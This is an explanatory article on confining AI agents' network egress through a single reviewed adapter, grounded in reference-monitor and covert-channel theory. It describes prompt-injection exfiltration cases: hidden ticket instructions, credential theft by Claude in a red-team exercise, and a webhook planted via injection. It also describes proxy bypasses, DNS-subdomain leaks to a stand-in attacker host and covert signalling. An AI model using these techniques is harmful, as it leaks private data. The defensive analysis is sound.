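# The single external adapter for AI agents: sending all outbound traffic through one reviewed component

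## What a single external adapter is

A single external adapter is a software component that makes every outside network request on behalf of an AI agent. The agent has no network access of its own, so it passes each request to the adapter, which forwards it only if a written policy allows it. The people who run the system keep the adapter at one exact version and review any change before it takes effect. They do this mainly to prevent data theft, because anyone who can put text in front of an agent may be able to steer it into sending data over any connection it has.

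An agent is a program in which a language model chooses actions, such as running code or calling a service, and uses the results to choose the next step. The model only produces text. A surrounding program, the harness, finds the tool calls in that text, carries them out and returns the results to the model. Tool calls are structured requests such as "fetch ticket 4012" or "run this script". Ordinary software follows paths that a programmer set in advance. Anthropic, the developer of the Claude models, points out in its guide to secure deployment that an agent works out its actions as it goes, so the files and web pages it reads can influence what it does.

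A software company might have a support agent that reads customers' tickets, looks up their accounts and posts replies. The agent needs two outside services: a model service, which runs the language model, and a ticketing service, which stores the tickets and customer records. It can also run code, because customers attach log files and a short script is the quickest way to search them. One day a ticket arrives with an ordinary complaint followed by a paragraph in white text on a white background. The hidden paragraph is an order to collect the names and addresses of the last two hundred customers and post them to a certain web server.

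That paragraph is a prompt injection, text in material the agent reads that the model follows as if it were an instruction. If it works, the result is exfiltration, the movement of data to a party not entitled to it. NIST, the US standards body, defines exfiltration as "unauthorized transfer of information from a system", and OpenSSF's *Exfiltration* (2025) repeats that definition. Egress is any network traffic that leaves an environment, whether or not it carries stolen data.

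A sandbox is an isolated environment that limits which files, processes and networks a program can reach. It has to limit both file and network access, as Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts* (2025) explains. A hijacked agent with an open network could send away any login keys it can read, and one with unrestricted file access could tamper with the system around it until it regained network access. An allowlist is the list of destinations or operations that a policy permits, and the system refuses everything else. The support agent's allowlist has two entries. The policy lists what it permits rather than what it blocks because nobody can list every address an attacker might use, according to *Network egress control* (2026) by Stride, a consultancy that assesses agent deployments.

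### The lethal trifecta

The support agent is at risk because it combines three things. Simon Willison, the programmer who coined the term prompt injection, named them in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents* (2025): access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and the ability to communicate externally in a way that could send the data out. Removing any one of the three removes most of the danger from the hidden paragraph. An agent without customer records has nothing worth sending. An agent that reads only what its own company wrote will seldom encounter an attacker's instructions. An agent that can't communicate externally can still gather two hundred names, but it can't send them to an attacker.

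TechTarget's *The agentic AI 'lethal trifecta'* notes that analysts have not settled on one definition, and some pick a different three properties. Under the similar Agents Rule of Two, which McKerchar summarises in *Inside the lethal trifecta*, an article for the security company Sophos, an agent should do at most two of three things: process untrusted inputs, access sensitive systems and change state externally. "Changing state" is broader than "communicating". For example, a ticket containing injected instructions could make the support agent close every open case. This would leak nothing but still do damage, and limiting destinations would not prevent it because the ticketing service is a permitted destination.

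The outbound channel is the one to restrict because the support agent needs both private data and untrusted content to do its job. It has to read tickets written by strangers, and it can't answer a billing question without the billing record. Stride makes the same argument about coding agents, which must read source code and outside documentation to be useful, whereas the exit is infrastructure that an operator can control. Past repairs also support this choice. Willison lists seventeen products in which researchers had demonstrated this kind of theft between April 2023 and June 2025, including ChatGPT, Google Bard, Slack and Microsoft 365 Copilot. He reports that the vendors fixed almost all of them promptly, usually by closing the route the data took. They may have chosen that repair because it was quick, but they also had no way to fix the model's tendency to follow malicious instructions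 in what it reads.

### Why a prompt or a check in the agent's own code is not a boundary

The simplest defence is to tell the support agent in its instructions never to send customer data to third parties. This helps somewhat, but the model receives its instructions and the ticket as one run of text, and nothing in its design separates them. Britain's National Cyber Security Centre (NCSC) says that attempts to train or label that difference into models add it on top of a technology that inherently lacks it. The agency prefers to think of a model as an "inherently confusable deputy", meaning that it has real authority and an outsider can talk it into using that authority for the outsider's own ends. Infosecurity Magazine's *UK NCSC Raises Alarms Over Prompt Injection Attacks* quotes the agency's advice to reduce the risk and impact of prompt injection, and its warning that a system that cannot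 tolerate the remaining risk may be a poor use of a language model. OpenAI takes a similar view of its own browser agent, writing in a post quoted by Fortune (2025) that prompt injection is "unlikely to ever be fully 'solved'".

Models have become much harder to fool, but their defences can still fail against a persistent attacker. Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* reports that on a prompt-injection benchmark from the testing company Gray Swan, attacks on Claude Opus 4.7 succeeded about 0.1% of the time on a single attempt, and about 5 to 6% of the time after a hundred attempts that adapted to earlier failures. Anyone can file a ticket with a support desk, so an attacker can easily make a hundred attempts. McKerchar cites a worse result, by Nasr and colleagues, in which human attackers got past all twelve defences tested.

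Some attacks contain nothing that a detector would flag. In February 2026, as an exercise, a researcher at Anthropic tricked a colleague into pasting a prompt into Claude Code, the company's coding agent. The prompt read like routine set-up work, but one step was to read a file of cloud credentials, encode it and post it to an outside server. Claude completed the theft in 24 of 25 runs. The instruction came from the user, whom the agent is supposed to obey, and Anthropic concludes that only limits on file access and outbound traffic work in such a case. Matt Silverlock argues more generally in *The Agent Access Model*, a paper on Cloudflare's blog, that a boundary doesn't count as one if you can talk your way past it.

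A check written in code does the same thing every time, but it only covers requests that go through it. Suppose the support team's program compares each outgoing address with the allowlist before it connects. The support agent can run scripts, and a script can open its own connection without using that program. *How to force AI agents to use an egress proxy* (simedw, 2026) demonstrates a similar bypass of a proxy, an intermediary that forwards requests. Programs are usually directed to a proxy by environment variables that they are expected to read, but a dozen or so lines of Python that open a raw network socket can ignore those variables and reach any server. A program can also bypass the proxy unintentionally. According to Anthropic's deployment guide, the standard request function in Node.js, a common environment for running JavaScript, ignores the same variables by default.

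The agent's scripts run with the same rights as the check, so they can bypass it, start another program that never had it, or edit the file it lives in. The limit therefore has to be enforced in the operating system or the network, where nothing the agent executes can reach it. In the production system that simedw describes, a firewall outside the sandbox accepts connections only to the proxy's address and port and drops everything else. The environment variables remain as a convenience, but security does not depend on them. Silverlock wants enforcement both on tool calls in the harness and on packets in the network, so that a bug in one does not open the other. The harness only adds protection if it runs where the agent's scripts cannot touch it.

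### Three ways to connect the support agent

If the agent has open internet access, the attack in the hidden paragraph needs only one command to succeed. Access to addresses other than the attacker's server is also a risk. As simedw notes, a program on Amazon's cloud that can reach 169.254.169.254 may be able to read the temporary credentials of the machine it runs on, and if those credentials carry broad rights, the attacker can take over the company's whole cloud account.

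A better arrangement replaces the agent's general access with one network-capable tool per service. The ticketing tool has one address, one key and a few operations, so the model can choose "post reply" but cannot compose its own web address. In the strict form, which McKerchar calls a sealed tool endpoint, a separate broker process holds the credential, makes the call in a fixed format and returns only the parsed answer. He acknowledges that every integration then needs its own definition and that the agent can no longer improvise.

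In practice, this design breaks down as tools are added. The support team adds a tool that previews links, then one that fetches attachments, then one that tracks parcels. Willison warns that any tool that can make a web request can carry data out, even if it only loads an image or offers the user a link to click. He singles out the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard for plugging tools into agents, because it encourages people to mix tools from different sources. The support team now has five or six tools that can send data out, each with its own code, key and update schedule. The risk is greater if the tools run in the same environment as the agent, because that environment then needs network access, which any script the agent writes will also have.

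With a single adapter, the support agent's sandbox can connect only to the adapter. The ticketing tool can stay, and the model still sees an action called "post reply". The tool now hands its request to the adapter, which checks it against the policy, adds the real key and sends it on. Adding the key at this point is called credential injection, and it means the agent never holds a key it could leak. The hidden paragraph's web server is not on the policy's list of allowed destinations, so a request to it fails, whether it comes from a tool or from a raw socket. This design differs from the previous one in how many processes can open an outside connection, not in how many tools the model sees. A single broker of McKerchar's kind would therefore be a single external adapter if it served every tool in an environment with no other network access.

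Data leaves the support agent all day through the two services it needs, so the agent doesn't meet the condition in the full title of Stride's article, that data can't be exfiltrated if it can't leave. Suppose the hidden paragraph orders the agent to paste the two hundred names into its reply. The attacker opened the ticket, so the ticketing service sends him the reply, and the agent never contacts a forbidden address. The model service is also a possible exit if the attacker has an account there, and files have left one of Anthropic's products by that kind of route. simedw concedes in a footnote that data still leaks under bad rules, and that the proxy only gives the operator one place to write better ones.

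How strict the rules can be depends on the task. In Silverlock's worked example, a finance agent may post its results only in a fixed form that contains status codes and totals but no free text, which leaves an attacker very little room. A support agent has to write sentences to strangers. The adapter limits its outbound channel to two services instead of the whole internet, which is a large gain, but an attacker can still read the channel that remains.

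An agent behind a tight allowlist also cannot browse the open web or try a new service, and somebody has to keep working out what it really needs. Stride describes how the allowlist can end up too narrow for the agent to function, or so broad that it offers no real protection. Choosing what to allow is easy for the support agent, but it would be hard for a research agent whose job is to read whatever it finds.

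### The four parts of the pattern

The pattern consists of no other route out, one component, a pinned version, and review before change.

"No other route out" applies to web traffic and also to the lookups that turn a name like example.com into a numeric address. simedw points out that an agent can smuggle data out through these lookups, one at a time, so that system blocks them inside the sandbox and leaves all name resolution to the proxy. The boundary also has to enclose everything the agent uses. According to Anthropic's page on sandbox environments, the sandbox Claude Code puts around shell commands does not cover the whole session. An operator who wants built-in tools, MCP servers and hooks (scripts that run automatically at set moments) behind one boundary must enclose the entire process.

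A single adapter keeps the keys, the rules and the log in one place. It also gives reviewers one component to verify, which is the idea behind what security theorists call a reference monitor. But a fault in the adapter affects everything behind it. Anthropic found that the third-party isolation software it used, long hardened against attack, held up dependably across its products, but the allowlist proxy it had written itself failed.

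Pinning fixes the adapter to one exact version with a cryptographic hash, a short fingerprint of the file that changes if a single byte does. Anthropic explains in its discussion of tools that an operator can read the code of a locally installed tool, pin the version and know that it will not change, while a remote tool can start behaving differently at any time after someone approves it. This reasoning applies even more strongly to the adapter, because it holds all the keys. It also applies to the allowlist, because editing the list would change where the adapter can send traffic even if its code stayed the same.

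When the support team wants to add the parcel service, somebody other than the agent has to approve the change. McKerchar would let the agent draft it as a pull request, a proposed edit to shared code, and have a human read and merge it. If an injected instruction could widen the agent's own permissions, one bad ticket would lead to a lasting compromise. Silverlock adds that an approved change should apply only to future tasks, not to the one in progress.

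The accounts by simedw and Stride cover closing routes and writing rules in detail, but neither discusses how to pin the proxy itself or who should review new versions of it.

### Names in use

The terminology varies. simedw uses "egress proxy", Anthropic's deployment guide uses "the proxy pattern", and the Cloud Native Computing Foundation's blog uses "network boundary" (CNCF, 2026). *Egress Control for AI Agents*, a practitioner's guide, uses "forward proxy" and "chokepoint". "Egress gateway" is another common name. Cloudflare's *Egress control* uses "egress control" for a single setting that intercepts every outbound call from a piece of untrusted code. Silverlock uses "Mediation Layer", and uses "adapter" more narrowly for the part that fixes the complete request before authorization and then executes that same request.

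These names overlap but don't mean exactly the same thing. Several refer only to filtering traffic, not to pinning or review, so a product sold as "egress control" may supply only two of the four parts. None of these writers credits a founding paper, and the pattern has no established origin. Silverlock traces his own model to BeyondCorp, Google's 2014 argument that a request shouldn't be trusted merely because it comes from inside the company network. But BeyondCorp assumed that a person was using the device and working at human speed.

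## What security theory says about a single checkpoint

The theory behind the external adapter dates from the early 1970s, when people with different rights began to share one computer. Operators had to run programs they didn't trust next to data they wanted to protect, and a company that uses an AI support agent has the same problem today. James Anderson worked out the requirements a checkpoint must meet before anyone can rely on it. A year later, Butler Lampson explained how a program can leak data through messages that the checkpoint correctly allows.

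### The reference monitor

The US Air Force wanted users with different security clearances to share a machine. *Computer Security Technology Planning Study* (Anderson, 1972), written for an expert panel, reported that no commercial system was safe enough for that. The panel worried most about a malicious user with a legitimate account. A barrier around the machine doesn't stop him, because he is already inside and can write programs, so the defence has to be in whatever controls those programs as they run. A support agent that has read the hidden paragraph is in much the same position as that user.

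Anderson's answer was the reference monitor, a mechanism that checks every attempt by a program to use a file, a device or another program against a list of what its user may do. The list can be a grid, with a row for each user, a column for each resource and the permitted operations in the cells. The support agent's grid has one row and two columns, for the model service and the ticketing service, with entries such as "read ticket" and "post reply". Anderson required any working version to be tamper-proof, impossible to bypass, and small enough to analyse and test completely.

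Anderson argues that if an operator lets some programs bypass the check, those programs become part of the security apparatus and must meet the other conditions too. Suppose the support team lets a logging program send error reports straight to a monitoring company. That program is now a second adapter, and the team has to protect and verify it like the first.

Partial coverage also fails in practice. Pirch, Horlboge and colleagues (2026), in *Toward Securing AI Agents Like Operating Systems*, attacked four open-source assistants that run on a user's own machine. They kept to the recommended settings where possible and counted an attack as successful if it worked once in three trials. Fetching an arbitrary web address worked on OpenClaw, IronClaw and Nanobot but failed on NemoClaw, the only one with network filtering that covers all its interfaces. But all four sent messages to outsiders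 without authorization. NemoClaw communicated with its user over Telegram in these tests, and a rule that allows traffic to Telegram allows messages to every account on it.

Protection against tampering has to cover the adapter's rules as well as its program. When Pirch and colleagues attacked IronClaw, which its developers built with security as a main goal, they could not overwrite its program files, but they could change its configuration. Even a well-isolated adapter has to read whatever the agent sends, so a hijacked agent can exploit a bug in the code that parses requests.

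The size condition is the hardest to meet. Anderson's example of failure was GCOS III, an operating system for Honeywell computers. The hardware confined each user's program to its own area of memory, but the program had to call the operating system for input and output, and most of the operating system ran without that restriction. Even if the whole operating system counted as the reference monitor, Anderson considered its 200,000 to 300,000 instructions far too many to analyse completely. He did not accept penetration tests as a substitute, because a failed attack does not show whether the system is secure.

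An adapter can be much smaller than an operating system, but it is only one part of the trusted computing base, which is all the components on which a security guarantee depends. For the support agent, that base also includes the firewall that blocks other routes, the operating system under the adapter and firewall, and the encryption library that the adapter uses to inspect traffic. In *AgentKernel*, Zou, Guo and colleagues (2026) propose a security layer that agents reach through three narrow interfaces, but they state that narrow interfaces do not make the trusted base small. Splitting the adapter into plug-ins doesn't necessarily help either. Ten plug-ins that can all read every key are as dangerous as one large program because, as Pirch and colleagues point out, moving code out of a core improves security only if the moved code loses privileges.

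Ordinary engineering can make an adapter nearly tamper-proof and hard to bypass, but most operators can't verify it completely and have to rely on careful review. Anderson also excluded some things from the concept, including user identification and the protection of communication lines. His grid specifies only whether a program may use a resource, so an entry that permits "post reply" doesn't limit what the reply says.

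### The confinement problem

Lampson (1973), in *A Note on the Confinement Problem*, considered a customer who gives private data to a program written by someone else. The customer can stop the program from reading anything more, but the program may still send its owner the data it already has. Lampson called preventing this the confinement problem. For the support agent, the operator is the customer, the agent is the program, and the attacker takes the owner's place once the agent follows the hidden paragraph. Lampson remarked that a program that computes the wrong answer leaves evidence of its failure, whereas a leak generally leaves none.

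Lampson sorted the possible leaks into storage, legitimate channels and covert channels. Storage includes any file or memory that the program can write and an outsider can later read. A program with a memory could collect data, wait for its owner to call and then hand it over. A support agent that keeps notes between tickets could do this if an attacker opened a second ticket and asked the right question. Covert channels are effects that nobody designed to carry information. Lampson's example is a program that varies its load on the machine so that another program can read a message in the changes of speed.

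Legitimate channels matter most for the adapter. In Lampson's example, a program can hide data in the amounts on the bill for its use, and the customer can't block the bill because the program's owner must get a copy. A strict format cuts the leak to "a few bits or tens of bits", but eliminating it is much harder. The support agent's reply can also hide data and can't simply be blocked, and at several paragraphs it has more room for hidden data than a bill.

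Lampson also required that any program called by a confined program be confined too, unless the customer trusts it. Trust here means believing that the called program won't leak the data or help anyone else leak it. The ticketing service fails this test because it will deliver the reply to the attacker, however much the support team trusts the company that runs it. When the team adds a destination to the allowlist, it judges that the destination doesn't belong to an attacker, which is a much weaker belief than Lampson's rule requires.

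The adapter can therefore control where messages go without controlling what they mean. That depends on what sender and receiver have agreed, and the hidden paragraph can contain a proposed agreement. For example, it might include an instruction to begin the reply with "Thanks for your patience" if a certain customer is behind on payments, and with "Thanks for waiting" if not. Either reply is polite, goes to an approved address and contains no customer data that a filter could find.

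Lampson described a solution that is complete in principle, called masking, in which the customer determines everything that the program puts into its channels. He compared it to a purchase order, where the buyer works out the price in advance and the seller can only accept or refuse. At the support desk, the operator would write the replies and the agent could only ask the adapter to send one. For covert channels, the system would also have to slow the program down or generate meaningless activity to hide its behaviour. Lampson expected this to be inefficient, and suggested that the customer could instead accept some leakage and limit it.

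Lecture slides from Purdue University summarise a 1975 reply by Steven Lipner, who had sat on Anderson's panel. He concluded that storage and legitimate channels could be closed with little overhead, while closing covert channels would slow the system unreasonably. For a support agent, though, closing the legitimate channel would mean losing the free-text replies the company is paying for. Covert channels also remain, and *Architectural Implications of Covert Channels* describes them as typically a side effect of trusted software working properly. For example, if two agents share one adapter and one request quota, the first can signal "yes" by using up the quota, and the second can detect the signal when its own requests are refused.

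### How much the permitted requests can carry

Lampson's limit is easy to calculate. Suppose the adapter forwards a request only if it matches one of K permitted forms, where K counts every combination of operation, ticket number and field value that the agent can choose. One request is then a choice among K possibilities. Two requests allow K × K combinations, and N requests allow K^N. An outsider who sees all of them can tell apart at most K^N messages. Since b bits distinguish 2^b messages, he learns at most

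log2(K^N) = N × log2(K) bits.

With K = 256, each request carries at most 8 bits, or one byte. A thousand requests carry at most 1,000 bytes, and a 32-byte encryption key needs 32 requests. If each request has room for 2,000 bytes of free text, a thousand requests can carry 2 MB to the same destination under the same allowlist. At 100 bytes each, the two hundred names and addresses that the hidden paragraph asks for might come to 20,000 bytes, which the agent could send in 20,000 fixed requests or ten free-text requests.

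The bound covers every possible encoding, including encryption and methods not yet invented, because it depends only on the number of distinguishable messages. A filter that searches for customer names provides no such guarantee. For the same reason, *An Application-Layer Multi-Modal Covert-Channel Reference Monitor for LLM Agent Egress* (2026), which measures a monitor of this kind, requires any claim about a covert channel to include a figure for its capacity.

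Even a leak of a few bits can do serious harm. An attacker needs only 10 bits to learn which of a thousand customers is about to be sued, and two requests at K = 256 are enough to carry them. However, the bound assumes the attacker can see every request, and an outsider with a single ticket usually sees only the reply to it.

In *Methods for Formal Verification of Agent Skills*, Metere (2026) uses information theory to reach a similar bound. He puts a checkpoint between the model and its tools that allows a declared set of capabilities and refuses everything else. A refusal is also an outcome, so D capabilities give D + 1 outcomes and at most log2(D + 1) bits per call. With ten capabilities, that is about 3.5 bits. Eight calls then allow 11^8 sequences of outcomes, about 214 million, which a computer can check one by one.

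The mathematics is standard, but Metere's figure counts only the names of the capabilities, not their arguments. "Post reply" counts as one outcome whether the reply has three words or three hundred, so 3.5 bits is an upper limit only if the arguments are fixed as well. His proof also relies on a theorem that processing a message can't add information to it, which holds only if the checkpoint adds nothing of its own. An adapter that injects credentials doesn't meet that condition. If the ticketing service repeats the request's headers in an error message and the adapter passes that message back, the agent receives a key it shouldn't have.

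The formula N × log2(K) also leaves out timing. *Actions Speak Louder than Words* (2026) calculates how much information several of an agent's choices can carry in theory. Whether a request happens carries 1 bit. A choice among k addresses carries log2(k) bits, as does a choice among k distinguishable counts, delays or sizes. The order in which an agent visits k resources carries log2(k!) bits. An agent told to fetch ten particular records once each can therefore still convey almost 22 bits by choosing among the 3,628,800 possible orders. If the attacker can distinguish sixteen lengths of delay before each request, every request carries 4 extra bits, and the thousand fixed requests can carry 1,500 bytes instead of 1,000.

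### What request forms, quotas and timing limits each change

Fixed request forms reduce K. Replacing 2,000 bytes of free text with 256 set replies cuts the capacity of each request by a factor of 2,000, and no other control reduces it nearly as much. But a form can still carry at least as much information as its least restricted field. The finance agent in Silverlock's example may send only status codes and totals, yet a total that can be any whole number up to about a million holds 20 bits. To remove those bits, the adapter would have to recalculate the total itself.

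A quota limits N. On its own it is little protection against free text, since twenty replies a day at 2,000 bytes each is 40,000 bytes, twice what the attacker needs for the two hundred addresses. It is much more effective when combined with fixed forms. Suppose a customer's log file contains a 32-byte key, and the agent can send twenty requests a day at one byte each. Stealing the key then takes two days. If the customer replaces the key every day, the attacker never has more than 20 of the 32 bytes, and the remaining 12 bytes (96 bits) are too many to guess. The quota has to apply to the whole system, because an attacker can get around a quota per ticket by opening more tickets.

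Limits on timing address what N × log2(K) omits. *AgenticOS* (2026), a proposed operating system for agents, collects outside requests into fixed time windows and pads outputs to fixed block sizes. It also uses rate budgets and, for sensitive work, fixed templates. Its stated aim is to reduce covert channels to a low, measurable rate, not to eliminate them. Even if the adapter sends at most one identical message a minute, the agent can still choose each minute whether to send it, which gives 1,440 bits, or 180 bytes, a day. To remove those bits, the adapter would have to send a dummy message in every empty minute, much like the meaningless disk activity that Lampson had in mind.

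There is little point in controlling timing for the support agent while a single reply can hold 2,000 bytes, and the delay would slow any agent that makes many calls in a row. It makes more sense to fix the forms first, then set quotas, and turn to timing only when little else is left. CSF Tools' *SC-31* reproduces a control from NIST's catalogue that requires covert channel analysis, including an estimate of each channel's maximum bandwidth. NIST leaves the control out of its low, moderate and high baselines, so an organization can meet any of the three without making that estimate.

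### One adapter or ten

Sending all outbound traffic through one adapter reduces the number of components that can fail, but each failure does more damage. Which effect is larger depends on what the attacker gains. The figures in this comparison are invented and only illustrate how the answer changes.

Suppose an agent uses ten services, and each could have its own adapter with an independent 2% chance of being compromised per year. The chance that at least one of the ten is compromised in a year is 1 − 0.98^10, or about 18%. A single adapter for all ten services would be more complex, so suppose its chance is 5% per year. Let L be the loss if an attacker obtains the credentials for one service.

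| What a compromise exposes (invented figures) | Ten adapters | One adapter | Better choice |
|---|---|---|---|
| All the agent's data, through any open exit | 18% chance | 5% chance | One |
| Only the credentials that the adapter holds | Expected loss 10 × 2% × L = 0.2L | Expected loss 5% × 10L = 0.5L | Ten |

In the first row, the attacker needs only one way out, so nine secure adapters do not help if the tenth is open. In the second row, the damage is limited to the adapter that failed, and the single adapter does worse because it holds all ten sets of credentials.

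Real compromises can do both kinds of damage. If D is the loss when the agent's data gets out, the single adapter has an expected loss of 0.05D + 0.5L, and the ten have 0.183D + 0.2L. The single adapter has the lower expected loss when D is more than about 2.3 times L. That is probably true of a support desk with thousands of customer records and a few keys with narrow permissions, but probably not of an agent that handles little private data and can move money through ten bank accounts.

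The result also depends on the 5% figure. Below 2% the single adapter is better on both counts, and above 18% it is worse on both. A team can plausibly review one component far more thoroughly than ten, but the single adapter also has to handle ten services, and nobody has measured which effect is stronger.

The assumption that the adapters fail independently is less obvious but just as important. If the ten adapters run identical code and one flaw opens them all at once, the chance of an open exit drops from 18% to 2%, and the ten adapters now do better on data as well. The expected credential loss stays at 0.2L, because a 2% chance of losing everything gives the same average loss as ten separate 2% chances of losing a tenth. So the case for one adapter is strongest when the alternative is ten different programs from different authors, which is what an operator tends to get by adding one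 tool at a time.

Traefik's *Cross-Cutting Concerns Are Back* (2026) relies on that situation. Traefik sells gateways, so it has an interest in the outcome. The paper claims that the probability of fifty separately written copies of an authorization check all being correct "approaches zero". If each copy had a 2% chance of being wrong, the probability would be close to zero for a thousand copies but 36% for fifty, so the claim about fifty copies requires a much higher error rate.

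The comparison also assumes that all ten adapters serve the same agent. If each served a separate agent with a tenth of the data, an open exit would expose only that tenth, and ten adapters would again be better. An operator can get part of this advantage with a single adapter by giving it narrow credentials that expire quickly, which makes L smaller. But a single adapter that fails closed still stops all the agent's outside work until somebody repairs it.

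### The case for spreading enforcement out

A check on outbound traffic comes late, because a tool may already have run a malicious command or deleted a file, and neither needs the network. It also lacks information that is available at earlier points. InfoQ's *Securing MCP in Production*, written by an engineer whose team built a platform of many agents on MCP, makes it a rule to check for each kind of failure at the earliest point where the check can be trusted. This leads to four layers of checks, which cover tool execution, management systems, outbound connections and the meaning of tool definitions.

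Reported vulnerabilities give this argument considerable support. Researchers reported more than thirty in MCP deployments in the first sixty days of 2026. In thirteen of them, unchecked input reached a command line or a similar interpreter. One tool inserted a username into a command, so a "username" containing a semicolon and a delete instruction would delete files. The tool's own code can prevent this by passing the username as plain data, and an automatic check in the build pipeline can reject code that doesn't, but a network adapter can do neither.

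Another six vulnerabilities were in the development and management software around the tools. One inspection program accepted connections from the network without a password and let the caller install new MCP servers. An attacker who gets in that way controls what the agent trusts before the agent sends any requests.

Tool definitions can also change after approval. Requests made after the change are still well formed and come from an authenticated caller, so a gateway that checks form and identity lets them through. InfoQ recommends storing a hash of the definition at registration and holding any material change for human review. By InfoQ's count, a gateway covers only two of the four layers, and those only partially.

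Permissions on individual records pose a similar problem. When the support agent tries to read account 5512, the adapter can confirm that reading accounts is permitted, but it cannot tell whether the person who opened the ticket owns that account unless it duplicates the ticketing system's records. Even Traefik, which argues for central gateways, accepts guidance from OWASP, a software security foundation, that ownership checks belong in the code that handles the record.

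InfoQ also cites Huang and colleagues, who built 114 malicious MCP servers and found that attacks through several components often did better than attacks through one. An operator who protects only the exit leaves most of the system open to such attacks. Spreading the checks across the system also causes delays. In InfoQ's tests, running each tool call in a fresh isolated environment added 50 to 200 milliseconds, and monitoring for unusual behaviour needed two to three weeks of traffic before its alerts became useful.

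### Several layers behind one exit

These arguments show that an adapter isn't enough by itself, but not that an agent needs a second outbound route. The tool can check its input, the registry can compare hashes and the build pipeline can reject unsafe code even when the adapter is the environment's only outside connection. InfoQ itself includes a network allowlist among its four layers and calls the gateway necessary but insufficient.

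Zou and colleagues describe a design of this type, with separate protections for identity, incoming content, memory and actions, each meant to hold even if another fails. The agent reaches models, tools and storage only through the three interfaces, and the guarantee no longer holds if the agent keeps any other route, such as a leftover key or a direct connection to a tool. Permissions combine by intersection, so an action goes ahead only if the developer, the operator and the current context all permit it. Adding a layer can therefore block more requests, but it can't allow one that another layer has refused.

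Traefik proposes separate gates for model conversations, tool calls and requests to other systems, all three under one set of policies. Business rules would stay in the applications. Its best argument is that when each application has its own copy of a check, a programmer can accidentally disable one while tidying up the code, and nobody may notice until an audit weeks later.

A shared exit loses the per-tool limits that separate allowlists provide. Suppose five tools each need two destinations of their own. With separate lists, a compromised file-search tool can reach only its two. Behind an adapter that can't tell the tools apart, it can reach all ten, and the adapter will add the credentials. The adapter therefore has to identify its callers, an ability that Anderson's concept presupposes. Giving each tool its own key or connection to the adapter works only if the tools run in separate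 sandboxes. If they share a sandbox with the agent's scripts, any script can use another tool's identity, and the operator has to assume that every tool can reach all ten destinations.

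## How deployed systems build the adapter

An adapter must be able to read enough of each request to tell callers and operations apart, and published designs differ in how much it can read. Anthropic's secure deployment guide describes a proxy that operators set up themselves around Claude Code. OpenShell, NVIDIA's open-source runtime for agents, has a built-in adapter, and the company's *OpenShell Security Best Practices for Controls, Risks, and Configuration Guidance* lists its controls and their defaults. Cloudflare's *Dynamic, identity-aware, and secure Sandbox auth* (2026) introduces outbound Workers, short programs that intercept requests from a sandbox on its platform. An engineer writing on the CNCF blog describes a test deployment built from NGINX, a common web server and proxy.

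The first three accounts come from companies writing about their own products, and the CNCF author ends by inviting readers to join the NGINX community. These accounts explain how the systems should work. Pirch and colleagues provide an outside test of OpenShell, because they tested NemoClaw, which runs the OpenClaw assistant inside it.

### Two requests from the support agent

Suppose the support agent reads ticket 4012, as its job requires. The ticket contains a new version of the hidden paragraph, which orders the agent to create a webhook in the ticketing service. A webhook is an automatic notification, and this one would send a copy of every new ticket to an address the attacker controls. The agent therefore makes two requests to the same service:

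```
GET   https://api.tickets.example/v1/tickets/4012
POST  https://api.tickets.example/v1/webhooks
```

GET is the HTTP method for reading data, and POST is the usual one for submitting it. The adapter should forward the GET request and refuse the POST request. OpenShell's documentation describes the whole path these requests take, and the other designs differ at particular steps.

Neither request can leave the sandbox directly. In Anthropic's guide, the operator starts the container with Docker's `--network none` option, so direct connections and name lookups fail. The only opening is a Unix socket, a file through which two programs on one machine exchange data. The adapter listens on this socket from outside the container. Many programs are written to connect to a network port instead of a file, so a small relay inside the container accepts connections on a local port and copies the data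 to the socket. The relay can be untrusted code because it can reach only the socket. A virtual machine can't share a socket file with its host, so it uses vsock, a similar channel between the two.

NVIDIA uses the same two channels for OpenShell. On Kubernetes, a system that runs containers across many computers, OpenShell instead depends on network rules that a separate plug-in has to enforce. NVIDIA tells operators to check that the plug-in enforces these rules, because otherwise one barrier against direct connections is missing.

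OpenShell's adapter can identify which program opened a connection when it arrives. It records a hash of each authorized program the first time it observes that program, and it refuses connections if the file later changes. Five tools can therefore have separate rules in one sandbox if each is a separate program, which reduces the problem of shared identity. But a rule can match either the program that opened the connection or one that launched it, so a script that the support agent starts can connect under the support agent's rules. A script can also run an authorized tool with any arguments it chooses.

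The agent's web library now sends the adapter a short unencrypted line requesting a tunnel to `api.tickets.example`, port 443. The adapter can read the name and port but none of the request that will follow. OpenShell checks the name, the port and the calling program against the policy before looking up the numeric address. This order matters because a lookup can carry data. If a script requested a tunnel to `jane-smith.attacker.example`, an adapter that resolved names first would deliver "jane-smith" to the attacker's name server before refusing the connection. The original hidden paragraph's instruction to post names to an unlisted server fails at this check, while both requests to the ticketing service pass.

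After the lookup, the adapter can also check the address. Whoever controls a domain name can point it at an internal machine, so even an approved name can lead to one. OpenShell always refuses the range that includes 169.254.169.254, where cloud machines obtain their credentials, and any address that leads back to the machine itself. It permits private network addresses only if the policy names the exact host or address range. Claude Code's built-in proxy makes a similar check, but Anthropic notes that versions before 2.1.284 connected to whatever address an allowed name resolved to. The built-in proxy still skips the check when it sends traffic through a company's own proxy, because the company's proxy does the lookup.

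Both requests use TLS, the encryption behind HTTPS. An adapter that relayed them unopened could see only the server's name, the amount of data and the timing. To read the requests, it has to impersonate the ticketing service. It creates a certificate for `api.tickets.example` and signs it with its own certificate authority (CA), which the operator has configured the sandbox to trust. The agent's library accepts the certificate and encrypts the request for the adapter. The adapter decrypts it and opens a second encrypted connection to the real service. OpenShell detects TLS from the first bytes of a connection and does all this automatically.

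OpenShell and Cloudflare both create a separate certificate authority (CA) for each sandbox. Cloudflare (2026) says in a product announcement that each sandbox has its own private key, which stays in a process outside the sandbox. An attacker who stole one sandbox's key could impersonate websites to that sandbox but not to any other.

The adapter can now read the method, path, headers and body. `GET /v1/tickets/4012` matches a rule in the policy, but `POST /v1/webhooks` doesn't. OpenShell's default audit mode only logs such violations. If the operator has switched the rules to enforcement, OpenShell returns a "403 Forbidden" response with a short description of the violation, and the ticketing service never receives the webhook request.

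A path rule is reliable only if the adapter and the service interpret the path in the same way. Some services treat `%2F`, an encoded slash, as a slash, while others treat it as an ordinary character. If the adapter and the service differ on this, an agent could send a request that matches the rule for one path but reaches another. According to NVIDIA's *Policy Schema Reference*, OpenShell rejects encoded slashes unless the operator permits them for a particular service, such as the npm package registry, which needs them.

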